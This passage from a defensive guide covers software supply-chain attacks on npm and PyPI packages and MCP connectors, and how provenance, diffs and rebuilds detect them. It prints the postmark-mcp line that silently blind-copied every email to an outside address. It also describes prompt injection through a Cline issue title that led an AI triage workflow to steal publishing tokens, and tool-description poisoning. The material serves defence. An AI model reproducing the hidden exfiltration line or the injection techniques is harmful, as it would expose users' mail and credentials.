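The malicious packages carried valid provenance attestations. Kurmi and Snyk both described the provenance as SLSA Build level 3, but according to SLSA, npm's built-in provenance reaches only level 2.

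The attack also depended on three things that level 3 forbids. A build for a stranger's pull request changed a cache that the release build used. Code inside the release build accessed the token that let it sign as TanStack. The pull request build also influenced a later build, because the malware survived in the cache.

SLSA has an interest in defending its own framework, but its argument here follows from rules it published before the attack. A build platform that met level 3 would have prevented the cache poisoning that started this attack, so authors still have a reason to move to a stricter platform.

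Level 3 provenance would not have made every TanStack release safe. A malicious library that entered the build through an ordinary dependency update could have changed the finished package without touching the cache or the signing token, and the provenance would still have been accurate.

### Red Hat: branches that existed for seconds

Three weeks later, on 1 June 2026, an attacker published malicious versions of more than 30 packages from Red Hat's `@redhat-cloud-services` collection. They contained another worm, called Miasma. The attacker had access to a legitimate maintainer's GitHub account, according to Boost Security's *Trusted Publishing, Untrusted Branch* (2026). Unlike the earlier attack, this one did not use a poisoned cache.

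The maintainer's account could not push directly to the `main` branch because Red Hat required a review first, but it could create other branches. The attacker created a branch, added a workflow that published malicious packages, and then deleted the branch. The nine branches whose lifetimes Boost Security recovered existed for between 1 and 73 seconds. Pushing to the branch started the workflow, so nobody had time to review it.

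npm accepted the uploads because it compares the workflow's filename but not its branch or contents. The attacker matched the filename that each repository used for its releases, such as `ci.yml` in one and `ci.yaml` in another. A brand-new file with the right name was as good as the real workflow.

The provenance recorded all this accurately. For version 3.6.1 of `@redhat-cloud-services/types`, these are the values that a user could have compared with the legitimate release process:

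| Field | Malicious release | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Repository | `RedHatInsights/frontend-components` | Pass |
| Workflow | `.github/workflows/ci.yaml` | Pass |
| Ref | `refs/heads/oidc-61fff775` | Fail, because legitimate releases come from `main` |
| Commit | `8bf05125` | Fail, because it is not on `main` |

npm has removed the package, but the record of that branch remains in Sigstore's public log. Neither npm nor the usual tools compared the ref with anything. A user who ran Cosign with a pattern ending in `@refs/heads/main$` would have rejected the release.

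Boost Security published its report during the attack and listed what it had not confirmed. It suspects that malware on the maintainer's computer stole the account credentials. Outsiders can't see Red Hat's npm settings, so Boost Security inferred from the successful uploads that the settings did not require a particular GitHub environment. The ref is in the signed record, so neither uncertainty affects it.

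Later that day the attacker began adding files to existing branches. The files would run malware when a developer opened the project in the code editor VS Code or in an AI coding agent such as Claude Code. Ana should therefore inspect unfamiliar commits on GitHub's website, or with plain `git` commands, before opening the project in a code editor or AI coding agent.

### SlugFest: a trusted name with a new owner

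Checking the ref doesn't help if someone else has taken over the whole repository. SlugFest, a flaw that let strangers take over abandoned repository names, affected more than 1,500 npm packages with over 10 million downloads in total. Adebayo (2026) reports in *npm Trusted Publishing flaw left 1,500 packages open to attackers* that Bloom Security discovered the flaw and that GitHub released a fix on 2 October, almost four months after receiving the report.

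Such a takeover would have defeated even the strict Cosign command from earlier. A stranger who registered the abandoned name `ternmail` could have reproduced every name in the signing identity, including the tag, without stealing a password or token. Only the permanent numeric IDs of the repository and its owner would have differed.

npm's 48-hour limit on unused trusted publishing entries is meant to prevent the same kind of takeover, according to The Hacker News' *GitHub Tightens npm Publishing After Flaw Left 1,500+ Packages Vulnerable to Hijacking* (2026). Until its first use, an entry has no permanent number for npm to compare.

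Bloom Security also reported blocking a customer's AI agent from installing one of the affected packages. Someone could have taken over the package, but that doesn't mean it was malicious. By Bloom Security's count, agents install about 70 packages a month on a typical company computer, not including dependencies. Few people are likely to check the provenance of that many packages by hand.

### A malicious connector with valid provenance

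The attacks continued on 28 August 2026, when attackers published ten malicious versions of `@7nohe/openapi-react-query-codegen`, a tool that generates code for web applications. All ten had valid provenance, according to Socket's *OpenAPI React Query Codegen Compromised in Mini Shai-Hulud npm Supply Chain Attack* (2026). This version of the worm could also spread through PyPI and RubyGems, according to Endor Labs' *Trojanized @7nohe/openapi-react-query-codegen Adds PyPI to a Self-Replicating npm Worm*.

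On 9 September an attacker targeted `@dforge-core/dforge-mcp`, an MCP server on npm. *Attackers Abuse npm Trusted Publishing in GHAPPIER Campaign* (Mascellino, 2026) summarises an investigation by the security company CloudSEK. The attacker used the maintainer's account for 105 minutes and, unlike the attacker at Red Hat, could push to the `main` branch. They changed the release workflow to run on any push to `main`, then changed it again to publish without anyone's involvement.

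Version 0.2.21 was the newest release for almost 36 minutes. Its provenance correctly named the project's repository and the attacker's commit, and it would have passed `npm audit signatures`. The malicious code, a loader that CloudSEK calls GHAPPIER, was a single line in a 99 KB file. It eventually gave the attacker remote control of the machine.

The loader ran when the MCP server started, not during installation, so blocking install scripts would not have protected someone whose AI application launched the connector. But a user who installed the package and checked it before starting it, as recommended earlier, would still have had a chance to notice something wrong.

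The best clue was probably how the run started. The attacker had to change the trigger, so earlier releases had presumably started differently, perhaps from a tag or by hand. Comparing the ref and `event_name` with those of an earlier version might have revealed the change. CloudSEK recommends version 0.2.22 and says that a lock file containing 0.2.21 is itself a sign of possible infection.

### Which checks would have failed

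The table compares three of these attacks with a possible attack through SlugFest before the fix.

| Check | TanStack | Red Hat | Attack through SlugFest | `dforge-mcp` |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Signature | Pass | Pass | Pass | Pass |
| Repository | Pass | Pass | The name passes, but the permanent number fails | Pass |
| Workflow file | Pass | Pass | Pass | Pass |
| Ref | Pass | Fail | Pass | Fail only if the user expects something other than `main` |
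| Run outcome | Fail | Not reported | Pass | Not reported |
| Build isolation | Fail | No protection, because the attacker wrote the workflow | No protection, because the attacker owns the repository | No protection, because the attacker changed the source |

Ana can't inspect build isolation directly. She has to rely on what she knows about the platform. The values for most of the other checks are in the provenance. If she has saved the bundle from npm as `connector-provenance.json`, this command prints them:

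```
jq '.dsseEnvelope.payload | @base64d | fromjson | .predicate
    | .buildDefinition.externalParameters.workflow,
      .buildDefinition.internalParameters,
      .runDetails.metadata.invocationId' connector-provenance.json
```

For Ternmail's version 1.4.2, the output might be:

```
{
  "ref": "refs/tags/v1.4.2",
  "repository": "https://github.com/ternmail/connector",
  "path": ".github/workflows/publish.yml"
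}
{
  "github": {
    "event_name": "push",
    "repository_id": "700000001",
    "repository_owner_id": "80000001"
  }
}
"https://github.com/ternmail/connector/actions/runs/9000000001/attempts/1"
```

The command reads the statement without verifying it, so Ana should run it after Cosign has verified the bundle. She can then do the same for an older release and compare the two. Only the version number in the ref should have changed, and the two permanent numbers should be the same. A legitimate move to another GitHub account would change at least the owner's number, so if either number differs, Ana should look for an announcement from Ternmail.

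She should take the expected numbers from the provenance of a release that predates any suspicion, rather than look up `ternmail/connector` on GitHub today. If a stranger had taken over the name, GitHub would return the stranger's numbers.

### What authors can change, and what users can see

Most of the protection against these attacks is in the hands of authors, GitHub and npm. A user can verify only some of it.

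| Measure | Who turns it on | Attack it would probably have stopped | What a user can verify |
|---|---|---|---|
| A GitHub environment limited to release branches or tags | The author, on GitHub and npm | Red Hat | The ref, but not the setting |
| Staged publishing | The author | Red Hat, `dforge-mcp` and perhaps TanStack | Nothing in the provenance, because the workflow signs it before the approval |
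| A read-only cache for untrusted triggers | GitHub, automatically | TanStack | Nothing in the provenance |
| An isolated builder | The author, for example through a shared workflow | TanStack | The builder's signing identity |
| Trust tied to the repository's permanent number | npm, automatically | An attack through SlugFest | The numbers in the provenance |

An environment would have stopped the Red Hat uploads, which came from throwaway branches, but not the other attacks. TanStack's malware ran in the official workflow on `main`, and the `dforge-mcp` attacker could push to `main`. An attacker who takes over an administrator's account may also be able to change the environment's rules.

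Snyk instead advises authors to add the branch to their trusted publishing entry on npm. Boost Security points out that neither npm nor PyPI has a field for this. Such a field would not have helped TanStack anyway, because its malicious packages came from the expected branch.

With staged publishing, the workflow uploads a release, but npm holds it until a maintainer approves it with a second factor, such as a code from a phone. An attacker who controls the workflow therefore also needs the maintainer's second factor to publish a release. *npm Trusted PublishingでOIDCを使ってトークンレスでCIからnpmパッケージを公開する* (azu, 2025), a Japanese guide updated in November 2026, describes workflows that stage releases with the command `npm stage publish`.

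Boost Security thinks staged publishing would have stopped the Red Hat attack completely. It might not have stopped the TanStack attack. The maintainers had just merged two fixes and may have been expecting new versions, so a busy maintainer might have approved the malicious ones without opening them. Approval is most useful if the maintainer first checks that the run succeeded and that the list of files looks normal. Package authors also have to turn the feature on, and many probably won't.

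InfoQ's *GitHub Hardens npm and Actions Defaults, Drawing Debate over Delays versus Signing* describes an argument about whether authors should sign packages themselves, as Linux distributions do. One Hacker News commenter complained that npm had rejected proposals for this for a decade, and another replied that a compromised build system would sign malicious packages too. Author signing could have blocked TanStack's automatic uploads, but only if the author kept the key off the build system and didn't blindly sign whatever the workflow produced, and if users required the signature. Staged publishing offers some of the same protection without requiring users to check another signature.

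GitHub's 2026 changes to its build service need less effort from authors. The read-only cache for untrusted triggers blocks the TanStack attack at its third step. GitHub also changed `actions/checkout`, the standard step for fetching source code. It no longer fetches code from strangers' copies of a project under the triggers attackers most often exploit, unless the author overrides this. GitHub updated older versions of the step as well, but a workflow that pins the step to an exact commit gets the change only when someone updates the pin.

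Other changes are optional. Administrators can restrict who may start a workflow and which triggers it may use. A firewall that records a build's network connections was still a technical preview in July. InfoQ observes that the automatic changes are moderate and that authors still have to opt in to the strongest protections.

When a package is built by an isolated builder, users can check that it came from that builder. Suppose Ternmail builds its connector with Buildguild's shared workflow, and malware gets into another job in `publish.yml`. If that job has permission to request an OIDC token, the malware can still upload a package, because npm checks only for the filename `publish.yml`. But the certificate would name Ternmail's workflow instead of Buildguild's, so Ana would reject the package if she required Buildguild's signing identity.

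This would not have helped at Red Hat, because an attacker who can write a workflow on a new branch can have it call the same shared builder and get a genuine signature. Ana therefore has to check the ref as well as the builder.

SLSA also recommends rebuilders, independent groups that build a package again from the same source on their own machines. If the build is reproducible, the two results should be identical. A rebuild of TanStack's packages would have differed from the malicious versions, because the malware came from the cache and not the official source code. Rebuilding `dforge-mcp` would probably not have revealed a problem, because the attacker had committed the malicious code to the repository.

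## What a verified build leaves unexamined

Suppose that version 1.4.2 of Ternmail's connector passes every check so far and that nobody tampered with its build. Ana then knows which commit the package came from, but not whether she can trust the commit's author. In September 2025, users of a real mail connector learned that they could not trust its author.

### postmark-mcp: one added line

Postmark is a service that sends email on behalf of other companies' software. It had put the source code of an MCP server on GitHub, but Postmark says it had not published the server on npm. Somebody else copied the code and uploaded it there as `postmark-mcp`. According to Koi, the security company that discovered the attack, versions 1.0.0 to 1.0.15 worked as expected. Version 1.0.16 added this line:

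```
Bcc: 'phan@giftshop.club',
```

From then on, every email that an AI agent sent through the connector also went to that address as a blind copy.

This package turned malicious within two days, although Koi warns that a tool can be legitimate for months first. The publisher uploaded it on 15 September and released the malicious version, 1.0.16, on 17 September, according to The Hacker News (2025). Semgrep's *So the first malicious MCP server has been found on npm* (2025) dates Koi's findings to 25 September, by which time the publisher had deleted the package. OSV, a public malware database, listed it a day later as *MAL-2025-47604* (2025). The malicious code was therefore available for about eight days. A three-day cooldown would only have delayed its installation, and a search of OSV during those eight days would have found nothing.

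Nobody knows how much mail the attacker received. Koi assumed that a fifth of the connector's 1,500 weekly downloads were in active use, and guessed from this that 300 organisations were using it to send a total of 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day. The Hacker News reports 1,643 downloads in total.

Users who approved each message before the agent sent it could still have missed the theft. Snyk's *Malicious MCP Server on npm postmark-mcp Harvests Emails* (2025) reproduces the code, in which the `sendEmail` tool has inputs for the recipient, subject and text, but none for blind copies. The connector added the blind-copy address after the agent called the tool, and its reply mentioned only the visible recipient.

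The `postmark-mcp` package almost certainly had no provenance. The `package.json` that Snyk reproduces lacks the `repository` field that npm requires for provenance, and ReversingLabs' scan of version 1.0.18 found no declared source repository either.

But the publisher could easily have obtained provenance by putting the copied code in their own public repository, committing the malicious line and releasing the package through GitHub Actions. The signature, digest, workflow, tag and commit would all have been correct. A stricter build platform would have made no difference, because it would have built the same malicious code.

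One check would have failed for a user who expected the package to come from Postmark's repository, `ActiveCampaign/postmark-mcp`. A user who had accepted the publisher's repository at version 1.0.0 would have seen no change at 1.0.16. If the publisher had written an original mail connector instead of copying one, users would have had no other repository to expect.

The package also named Jabal Torres as its author. Torres writes about the genuine server on Postmark's blog, so the impostor presumably copied the name along with the code. Postmark now publishes an official package, `@activecampaign/postmark-mcp`.

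Choosing the official package excludes impostors, but attackers can compromise official packages too. In November 2025, malicious versions of `@postman/postman-mcp-server` appeared on npm, according to OSV's *MAL-2025-190909* (2025). Postman, a developer tools company, is unrelated to Postmark.

### The packages beneath the connector

Ternmail's provenance covers only its own package, and npm chooses the versions of the dependencies during installation.

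On 8 September 2025 an attacker took over the npm account of Josh Junon, a package maintainer. Junon had received an email that appeared to come from npm and asked for updated two-factor authentication details, according to The Hacker News (2025). The attacker then published malicious versions of 20 packages that together had more than two billion downloads a week.

Some of these packages were indirect dependencies of the official MCP TypeScript SDK, the library that many npm connectors use to implement the protocol. Stacklok's *Examining the impact of npm supply chain attacks on MCP* concludes that any connector built with the SDK was potentially vulnerable. Suppose Ternmail had released its connector a month earlier, with perfect provenance. A user who ran it through npx that morning would have received a clean version of `debug`, a small logging library. A user who ran the same connector,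 with the same attestation, that afternoon and without a cached copy could have received the malicious version 4.4.2.

The exposure lasted two and a half hours, according to GitLab's *GHSA-qj3p-xc97-xw74* (2025), an advisory for another package that uses `debug`. Existing lock files protected users who did not update them during that time. Narrow version ranges did not help much, because the attacker numbered the malicious releases as small fixes.

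The malware in `debug` probably did no harm to ordinary connectors. It redirected cryptocurrency payments inside web browsers, and GitLab's *CVE-2025-59144* (2025) states that it did not affect servers or programs running locally. Stacklok calls containers an effective defence in this incident, but the incident is a poor test of them because the malware did nothing outside a browser.

The LiteLLM attack of March 2026 reached a user through a connector. FutureSearch (2026), an AI company, discovered the malicious version 1.82.8 after an MCP plugin in the code editor Cursor had installed it as an indirect dependency. A follow-up, *How a Poisoned litellm Package Compromised an MCP Server in Cursor*, explains that uvx had downloaded the library because nobody had pinned its version. The first sign was a powerful Mac slowing almost to a halt. The package's `litellm_init.pth` file runs whenever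 Python starts in that environment, so the connector didn't have to use the library to trigger it.

To check the whole tree, Ana first needs to know which packages lack provenance. In the folder with her lock file, these commands compare the full list with the packages that `npm audit signatures` has verified:

```
jq -r '.packages | to_entries[] | select(.key != "")
    | (.key | sub("^.*node_modules/"; "")) + "@" + .value.version' \
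  package-lock.json | sort -u > all.txt

npm audit signatures --json --include-attestations \
  | jq -r '.verified[] | "\(.name)@\(.version)"' | sort -u > attested.txt

comm -23 all.txt attested.txt
```

The last command prints the packages without a verified attestation. The output may include a few packages for other operating systems, which npm lists in the lock file but doesn't install. For the packages in `attested.txt`, Ana still has to compare each repository with the one she expects, as she did for the connector. She can save that list of repositories, and after an update she needs to check only the packages whose versions changed.

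If an unfamiliar package such as `debug` turns up, `npm explain debug` shows which packages brought it in. For Python, `uv tree --invert --package litellm` does the same for `litellm`.

Some developers bundle their libraries into a single file before publishing. The bundled code becomes part of the connector's package, so neither Ana's lock file nor `npm audit signatures` lists it separately. She would have to check Ternmail's lock file at the commit named in the provenance to see which library versions were bundled.

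### Code and instructions from outside the package

Even a complete check of the dependency tree covers only the files that npm supplied. Matthew Suozzo, who works on Google's OSS Rebuild project, recorded the network traffic of an npm installation for a 2026 talk. The installation contacted GitHub as well as the npm registry, and downloaded a prebuilt binary for the machine. An attestation for the npm package doesn't cover that binary, and whoever controls the download address may be able to replace the binary later.

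npm 12's block on install scripts prevents some of these downloads, but it can't stop a connector from downloading code after it starts. A connector could run normally for a month, then fetch a new module and execute it, while its digest stayed the same.

Many local connectors also pass most of their work to a remote service. Ternmail's connector would send each search to Ternmail's servers, and their operator can change how they handle mail without releasing a new package. The provenance covers only the program on Ana's machine. Even the address of a remote connector can change, as the registry census found.

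A third route is specific to AI agents. The connector sends the AI application the names and descriptions of its tools, which the application puts in the model's context. *MCP-DPT* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) points out that these texts influence the model before any tool runs. In tool poisoning, an attacker hides instructions in a description. For example, the description of Ternmail's search tool could include an instruction to put the user's passwords in every query. In a "rug pull", a connector behaves well until the user has approved it and then changes.

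If the descriptions are fixed text in the source code, anyone who reads the attested commit can see them. But a connector can also download them, or change them after a certain date. Ana can save the list that the connector really sends by using the MCP Inspector, a testing tool from the protocol's developers:

```
npx @modelcontextprotocol/inspector --cli \
  node /home/ana/ternmail/node_modules/@ternmail/connector/dist/index.js \
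  --method tools/list > tools-1.4.2.json
```

She can repeat this later and compare the two files. The command starts the connector, so she should run it only after the other checks, and preferably with a test account. The Inspector is also an npm package, so she should check and pin it too.

A malicious connector could pass this test by sending the Inspector a harmless list and the real AI application a different one. It could tell the two apart by the name and version that applications give when they connect, which Postmark says its official server records to identify traffic in its logs. The application is therefore a better place for the comparison. Rostamzadeh and colleagues also consider it especially well placed to block harmful actions, because it has access to both the tool descriptions and the model's planned actions. However, when they mapped existing defences, they found persistent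 gaps in that layer.

### Reading the source at the attested commit

npm states that provenance does not guarantee that a package is free of malicious code, and describes it as a link to source code that developers can audit. The link matters because it is easy to review the wrong code. A careful user of `postmark-mcp` might have looked for its source on GitHub, found Postmark's genuine repository and read every line without finding anything wrong. Provenance would have led that user to the publisher's own repository, where the extra line was visible.

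Ana can inspect the attested commit without opening the project in an editor:

```
git clone --no-checkout https://github.com/ternmail/connector
cd connector
git show 4e7d19c:package.json
git grep -nE "child_process|eval\(|fetch\(|https?://" 4e7d19c
```

The last command finds places where the connector may start other programs, run text as code or contact a web address. These are good places to start reading, but the search doesn't replace reading the code. It would have missed the malicious line in `postmark-mcp`, which contains none of these patterns and stole mail through Postmark's normal service. For a mail connector, Ana should read the function that builds each message and compare every field with the tool's inputs. The malicious line was on line 231 of a single file, so a patient reader could have reached it.

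She should also check that the version number in `package.json` is 1.4.2. Some release workflows start from one commit, add a second that updates the version number, and publish the result, but the provenance names only the first commit. *No Snake Oil* (Dietrich, White and colleagues, 2026) reports this in `freezegun`, a Python testing library, where the attestation for version 1.5.2 pointed to a commit that still declared version 1.5.1. In such a case she would have to find the later commit and review it too.

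For an update, Ana can limit her reading to what changed. The first command below compares the source at the two attested commits, where `91be03a` is the commit for version 1.4.1. The second compares the published packages without running them:

```
git diff 91be03a 4e7d19c

npm diff --diff=@ternmail/connector@1.4.1 \
  --diff=@ternmail/connector@1.4.2
```

Snyk found that the only notable difference between versions 1.0.15 and 1.0.18 of `postmark-mcp` was the blind-copy line, so `npm diff` would have exposed it almost immediately. For Python, a reviewer can unpack the two wheels and run `diff -r` on the folders, which would have revealed the new `.pth` file in the LiteLLM attack.

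The two comparisons are most useful together. If the source diff shows a three-line correction to the search tool and the package diff also shows a new 2 MB file, something other than the commit changed the package. If both show only the correction, Ana can be fairly confident in the update, as long as the earlier version was sound.

A developer would find it hard to review the code changes in a hundred dependencies, and minified JavaScript can make even a small change unreadable. A SLSA source attestation could show that other people had reviewed the commit, though not how carefully.

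### Rebuilding the package and comparing the results

Reviewing a package's source code is useful only if the package was built from that code. Provenance is the build platform's attestation that it was. Rebuilding the package on another machine and comparing the two builds checks that attestation.

For Ternmail's connector, Ana could run these commands in the cloned repository, inside a disposable virtual machine because the build runs other people's code:

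```
git checkout 4e7d19c
npm ci && npm run build && npm pack
mkdir published rebuilt
tar -xzf ../connector-1.4.2.tgz -C published
tar -xzf ternmail-connector-1.4.2.tgz -C rebuilt
diff -r published rebuilt
```

Here `connector-1.4.2.tgz` is the package she downloaded from npm. If `diff` prints nothing, the files have the same contents, even if the two archives have different digests. *Reproducibility is Not Enough* distinguishes three degrees of match:

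| Match | What is the same | What may differ |
|---|---|---|
| Byte-identical | The whole archive | Nothing |
| Content-identical | The contents of every file | Timestamps, file order and compression |
| Code-identical | Everything except known descriptive data | For instance, documentation or the recorded version of a build tool |

A match at any of these levels is strong evidence that nobody inserted code during the original build. To escape detection, an attacker would have to tamper with both builds in the same way, or commit the malicious code to the source, as in the `dforge-mcp` attack. A rebuild of `postmark-mcp` from Postmark's repository would have differed from the published package by the blind-copy line.

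A mismatch is much harder to interpret, because legitimate packages often fail to match their rebuilds. The same study automatically rebuilt thousands of packages. For npm packages without provenance, 50.9 percent of the rebuilds reached the comparison stage and 52.9 percent of those matched, or about 27 percent of the sample. For npm packages with provenance, 72.4 percent reached that stage and 73.2 percent of those matched, or about 53 percent of the sample.

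Most of that improvement did not come from the provenance. When the researchers ignored the attestations and guessed each package's commit from tags and version numbers, the share of attested npm packages that matched fell by only 1.5 percentage points. Projects that publish provenance evidently tend to have tidier builds. Guessing works well for an honest project, but an attacker who controls a repository can move its tags, so a signed record is safer for a security check.

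The researchers also looked for the causes of imperfect matches. Three types accounted for 61 percent of the causes they identified: different versions of build tools or libraries, files that the project's workflow generated, and changes that the workflow made to the source. In one Python package, the original build used version 3.2.3 of Cython, a tool that translates Python into C. The rebuild used version 3.2.6 and produced different C files. Rerunning the project's own workflow helped with only four of the 105 npm packages on which the researchers tried it.

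Ana should therefore check which files differ. A different timestamp or tool version is usually harmless. If `dist/index.js` contains extra code that she can't trace to the source or workflow, that is a reason not to run the package.

Software can make some of these judgements. Dietrich and colleagues studied 10,449 releases on PyPI that contained only Python code. OSS Rebuild could rebuild 56.5 percent of them, and 19.1 percent of the rebuilt wheels were byte-identical to the published ones. Many differences were in descriptive files. Every wheel also lists its files' digests, so a harmless change to one file changes that list too. The researchers' own tool ignores such differences, and it found 78.9 percent of the OSS Rebuild wheels equivalent, counting only those whose source code matched. An attacker could hide a malicious change in any difference that a tool ignores, so the rules have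 to be narrow. This tool records the reason for everything it discards.

Few users will rebuild packages themselves, and OSS Rebuild is meant to do it for them. It works out how to build a package, rebuilds it, discounts differences such as compression, and publishes signed SLSA provenance if the result matches, as Suozzo explained in *Introducing OSS Rebuild* (2025). Authors don't have to take part, and even a package released from a laptop can qualify. These commands list the rebuilt versions of `absl-py`, a Python library, and fetch the record for one of them:

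```
oss-rebuild list pypi absl-py
oss-rebuild get pypi absl-py 2.0.0
```

Google announced *OSS Rebuild* in July 2025 with provenance for thousands of packages. According to Google, the project rebuilds only the most popular packages in each registry, so a small company's connector is unlikely to be among them. It is more likely to cover some of the libraries the connector depends on.

Its success rate also varies. *Reproducibility is Not Enough* reports tests in which it verified 46 of 100 npm packages that it already tracked and 34 of 100 other popular ones. For PyPI the figures were 26 and 25. A missing record can mean that the package contains code from outside its repository, but the cause is usually more mundane, so Ana shouldn't treat a missing record as a warning.

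Suozzo's talk also described a case in which a successful rebuild wrongly suggested that a package was safe. An attacker spent years gaining control of xz, a compression tool, and hid a backdoor in it. Part of the malicious code was in the source archive that the Linux distribution Debian used to build its package, so independent rebuilds from that archive reproduced the backdoor exactly.

OSS Rebuild responded by recording what happens during a build as well as comparing the result. The xz build read test files even though the tests were switched off, which earlier versions had not done, and a simple program for displaying the beginning of a file wrote compiled code. These records are less informative when most of the work happens inside an interpreter such as Python's, which Suozzo described as a major challenge. Builds of JavaScript connectors, which run in Node.js, probably have the same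 problem.

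## What to do when an attestation is missing or weaker than before

Most of the checks so far start from an attestation, but Ana will often find that there isn't one. Her next step depends on the package's history. If Ternmail has never published an attestation, she can learn very little from its absence in the newest version. If every release for the past year had one and the newest doesn't, somebody may have uploaded the package with a stolen token or account, without using Ternmail's build workflow.

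### Packages that never had attestations, and packages that stopped

*A Difference Without a Distinction* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) reports that among npm packages with at least four releases between April 2024 and September 2026, 51.4 percent of the popular ones and 25.9 percent of a roughly random selection had provenance. On PyPI, 40 to 53 percent of popular packages and 20 to 32 percent of the others had attestations, depending on the sample. The study of whole registries mentioned earlier found far lower shares, probably because it also counted packages that rarely have new releases.

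Some careful projects deliberately avoid attested builds. The OpenJS Foundation looks after many widely used JavaScript projects, and its *Publishing More Securely on npm* advises small teams with critical packages to publish from their own computers with two-factor authentication. It recommends holding off on trusted publishing, partly because npm had no good way to require a second factor for such uploads. npm has since introduced staged publishing, which requires one, but some maintainers may still follow the older advice. If a project switched from attested builds to manual publishing for this reason, its next release would look just like an attacker's upload.

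Far fewer packages stop publishing attestations than never publish them at all. Of 188 npm and PyPI packages whose stable releases had ever carried provenance or an attestation, 19, or about one in ten, later published a stable release without it. Most of these lapses were presumably innocent. Ana can still reasonably treat each one as suspicious, because waiting a few days for an explanation is a small inconvenience and a malicious mail connector could compromise her whole mailbox.

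npm's public metadata shows which situation applies. This command lists the connector's five latest releases in order of publication:

```
curl -s https://registry.npmjs.org/@ternmail%2Fconnector \
  | jq -r '.time as $t | .versions | to_entries
      | sort_by($t[.key]) | .[-5:][]
      | [$t[.key][0:10], .key,
         (if .value._npmUser.trustedPublisher then "trusted publisher"
          elif .value.dist.attestations.provenance then "provenance"
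          else "none" end)] | @tsv'
```

The output might be:

```
2026-08-03    1.3.0    trusted publisher
2026-09-14    1.4.0    trusted publisher
2026-10-20    1.4.1    trusted publisher
2026-11-12    1.4.2    trusted publisher
2026-11-19    1.4.3    none
```

Here Ana should stay on 1.4.2. If all five lines ended in "none", Ternmail would simply be a project without attestations. For a Python connector, she can repeat the Integrity API request for a file from the previous release. If PyPI returns a provenance object for the old file and an error for the new one, the attestations have stopped.

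### Axios: two releases without the usual evidence

Axios is a library for making web requests, and many JavaScript programs depend on it. On 31 March 2026 an attacker published two malicious versions from the lead maintainer's npm account. Solar Designer (2026), in *Axios Supply-Chain Attack [v1.14.1] [0.30.4]*, quotes the maintainer's explanation. Someone posing as the founder of a real company had invited the maintainer to a convincing Slack workspace and then to a video meeting. During the meeting, a message said something on the maintainer's computer was out of date. The maintainer installed the supposed fix, which was malware that gave the attacker control of the machine.

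Version 1.14.1 appeared at 00:21 UTC. Version 0.30.4, for the older 0.x line, followed 39 minutes later. Both added a new dependency, `plain-crypto-js`, that contained the malware. npm removed the two versions at 03:15.

Trend Micro reports that every legitimate 1.x release came through GitHub, and Santos-Grueiro found that earlier releases had a trusted publisher. The malicious ones had neither a trusted publisher nor provenance:

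| Malicious version | Its evidence | The previous release on the same line | The strongest evidence on any earlier release |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1.14.1 | None | Trusted publisher | Trusted publisher |
| 0.30.4 | None | None | Trusted publisher |

The result for 0.30.4 depends on which earlier release the user compares it with. The maintainers had published 0.30.3 by hand from the same npm account, so a user who compared only those two would have seen no change.

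Adventures in Nodeland's *Why “Trusted Publishing” Can’t Save Us from Social Engineering* (2026), by a Node.js maintainer whom the same attackers had also approached, is more pessimistic. It argues that npm and GitHub can't distinguish a maintainer from an attacker who controls the maintainer's computer, and that the malicious axios release would have been signed too if axios had used trusted publishing. According to Santos-Grueiro, axios did use it, and the evidence was missing because the attacker bypassed it. But the argument holds for a more patient attacker. Datadog Security Labs reports that the axios attacker also had access to the maintainer's GitHub account and might have been able to start the official release workflow. The attacker could therefore perhaps have published the malicious release with the evidence that was missing.

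### Cline: a similar attack with an unclear history

On 17 February 2026, someone used a stolen npm token to publish version 2.3.0 of the command-line tool for Cline, an AI coding agent. According to Cline's *Post-mortem*, the only changes were the version number and an install script that added OpenClaw, a legitimate AI agent that users had not asked for. The release stayed up for about eight hours, and roughly 4,000 people or machines downloaded it.

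The theft probably began with another AI agent. In December 2025 Cline added a workflow in which Claude sorted incoming issues and could run commands on the build machine. Anyone with a GitHub account could put instructions for the agent in an issue's title. An attacker could use this to poison the cache of the nightly release workflow and steal its publishing tokens. A researcher reported the flaw on 1 January and published it on 9 February after getting no answer. Cline removed the workflow within 30 minutes, but then deleted the wrong npm token and left the exposed one active.

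Cline 2.3.0 had no provenance, and earlier stable versions may not have had it either. *Cline Supply Chain Attack Detected* (Likhith, 2026) says that all previous legitimate releases came through trusted publishing, which would make this the same pattern as axios. Cline's own statements suggest otherwise. Its post-mortem says that versions from 2.4.0 "now include" attestations. *Clinejection*, by the researcher adnanthekhan, also reproduces a message of 11 February in which Cline wrote that "authorized Cline org accounts" had published all the npm versions. Releases made through trusted publishing would normally show GitHub Actions as the publisher instead.

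The registry data doesn't settle the matter either. *Supply Chain Attack targeting Cline installs OpenClaw* (Plate, 2026) compares version 2.3.0 with a nightly test build, `2.2.3-nightly.1771330659`, which has a trusted publisher and provenance. But if the last number is a Unix timestamp (the seconds since the start of 1970), that build dates from 12:17 UTC on 17 February, 51 minutes after the malicious release, so it can't show what users could have expected beforehand. A rule that looks for weaker evidence might therefore have had nothing to compare with 2.3.0, whereas waiting a day before installing new releases would have kept it out.

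### How pnpm's no-downgrade rule works

pnpm, the alternative to npm mentioned earlier, can make this comparison automatically. Since November 2025 it has had a setting called `trustPolicy`. With the value `no-downgrade`, pnpm refuses a version whose evidence is weaker than that of an earlier one. The setting is off by default.

To check a stable version, pnpm takes all the stable versions that the maintainers published before it, whatever their numbers, and finds the strongest evidence among them. If the new version has less, the installation fails. The ranking has changed over time:

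| Evidence, strongest first | pnpm 10 | Since pnpm 11.5.0 |
|---|---|---|
| Staged publish that a maintainer approved with a second factor | No separate rank | Highest rank |
| Trusted publisher and provenance | Highest rank | Second rank |
| Trusted publisher without provenance | Highest rank | Counts as no evidence |
| Provenance without a trusted publisher | Second rank | Third rank |
| None | Lowest rank | Lowest rank |

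Comparing each release with the strongest evidence in the package's whole history helps catch repeated attacks. If pnpm had compared each release only with the one published just before it, it would have caught axios 1.14.1 but missed 0.30.4, because neither 0.30.4 nor the malicious 1.14.1 had any such evidence. In the attacks that Santos-Grueiro reconstructed, this narrower comparison would have caught 5 malicious releases instead of 17.

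According to pnpm's release notes, the check reads three fields in npm's metadata: the publication time, the trusted publisher and the provenance entry. pnpm can use them to determine whether evidence exists, but not whether the provenance names the right repository.

Older versions of pnpm applied the rule only when selecting a package version, so a version already in the lock file could bypass it. Since 11.1.3, pnpm also checks the lock file before downloading anything and stops with the error `ERR_PNPM_TRUST_DOWNGRADE` if a version fails. The `trustLockfile` setting turns off this lock file check.

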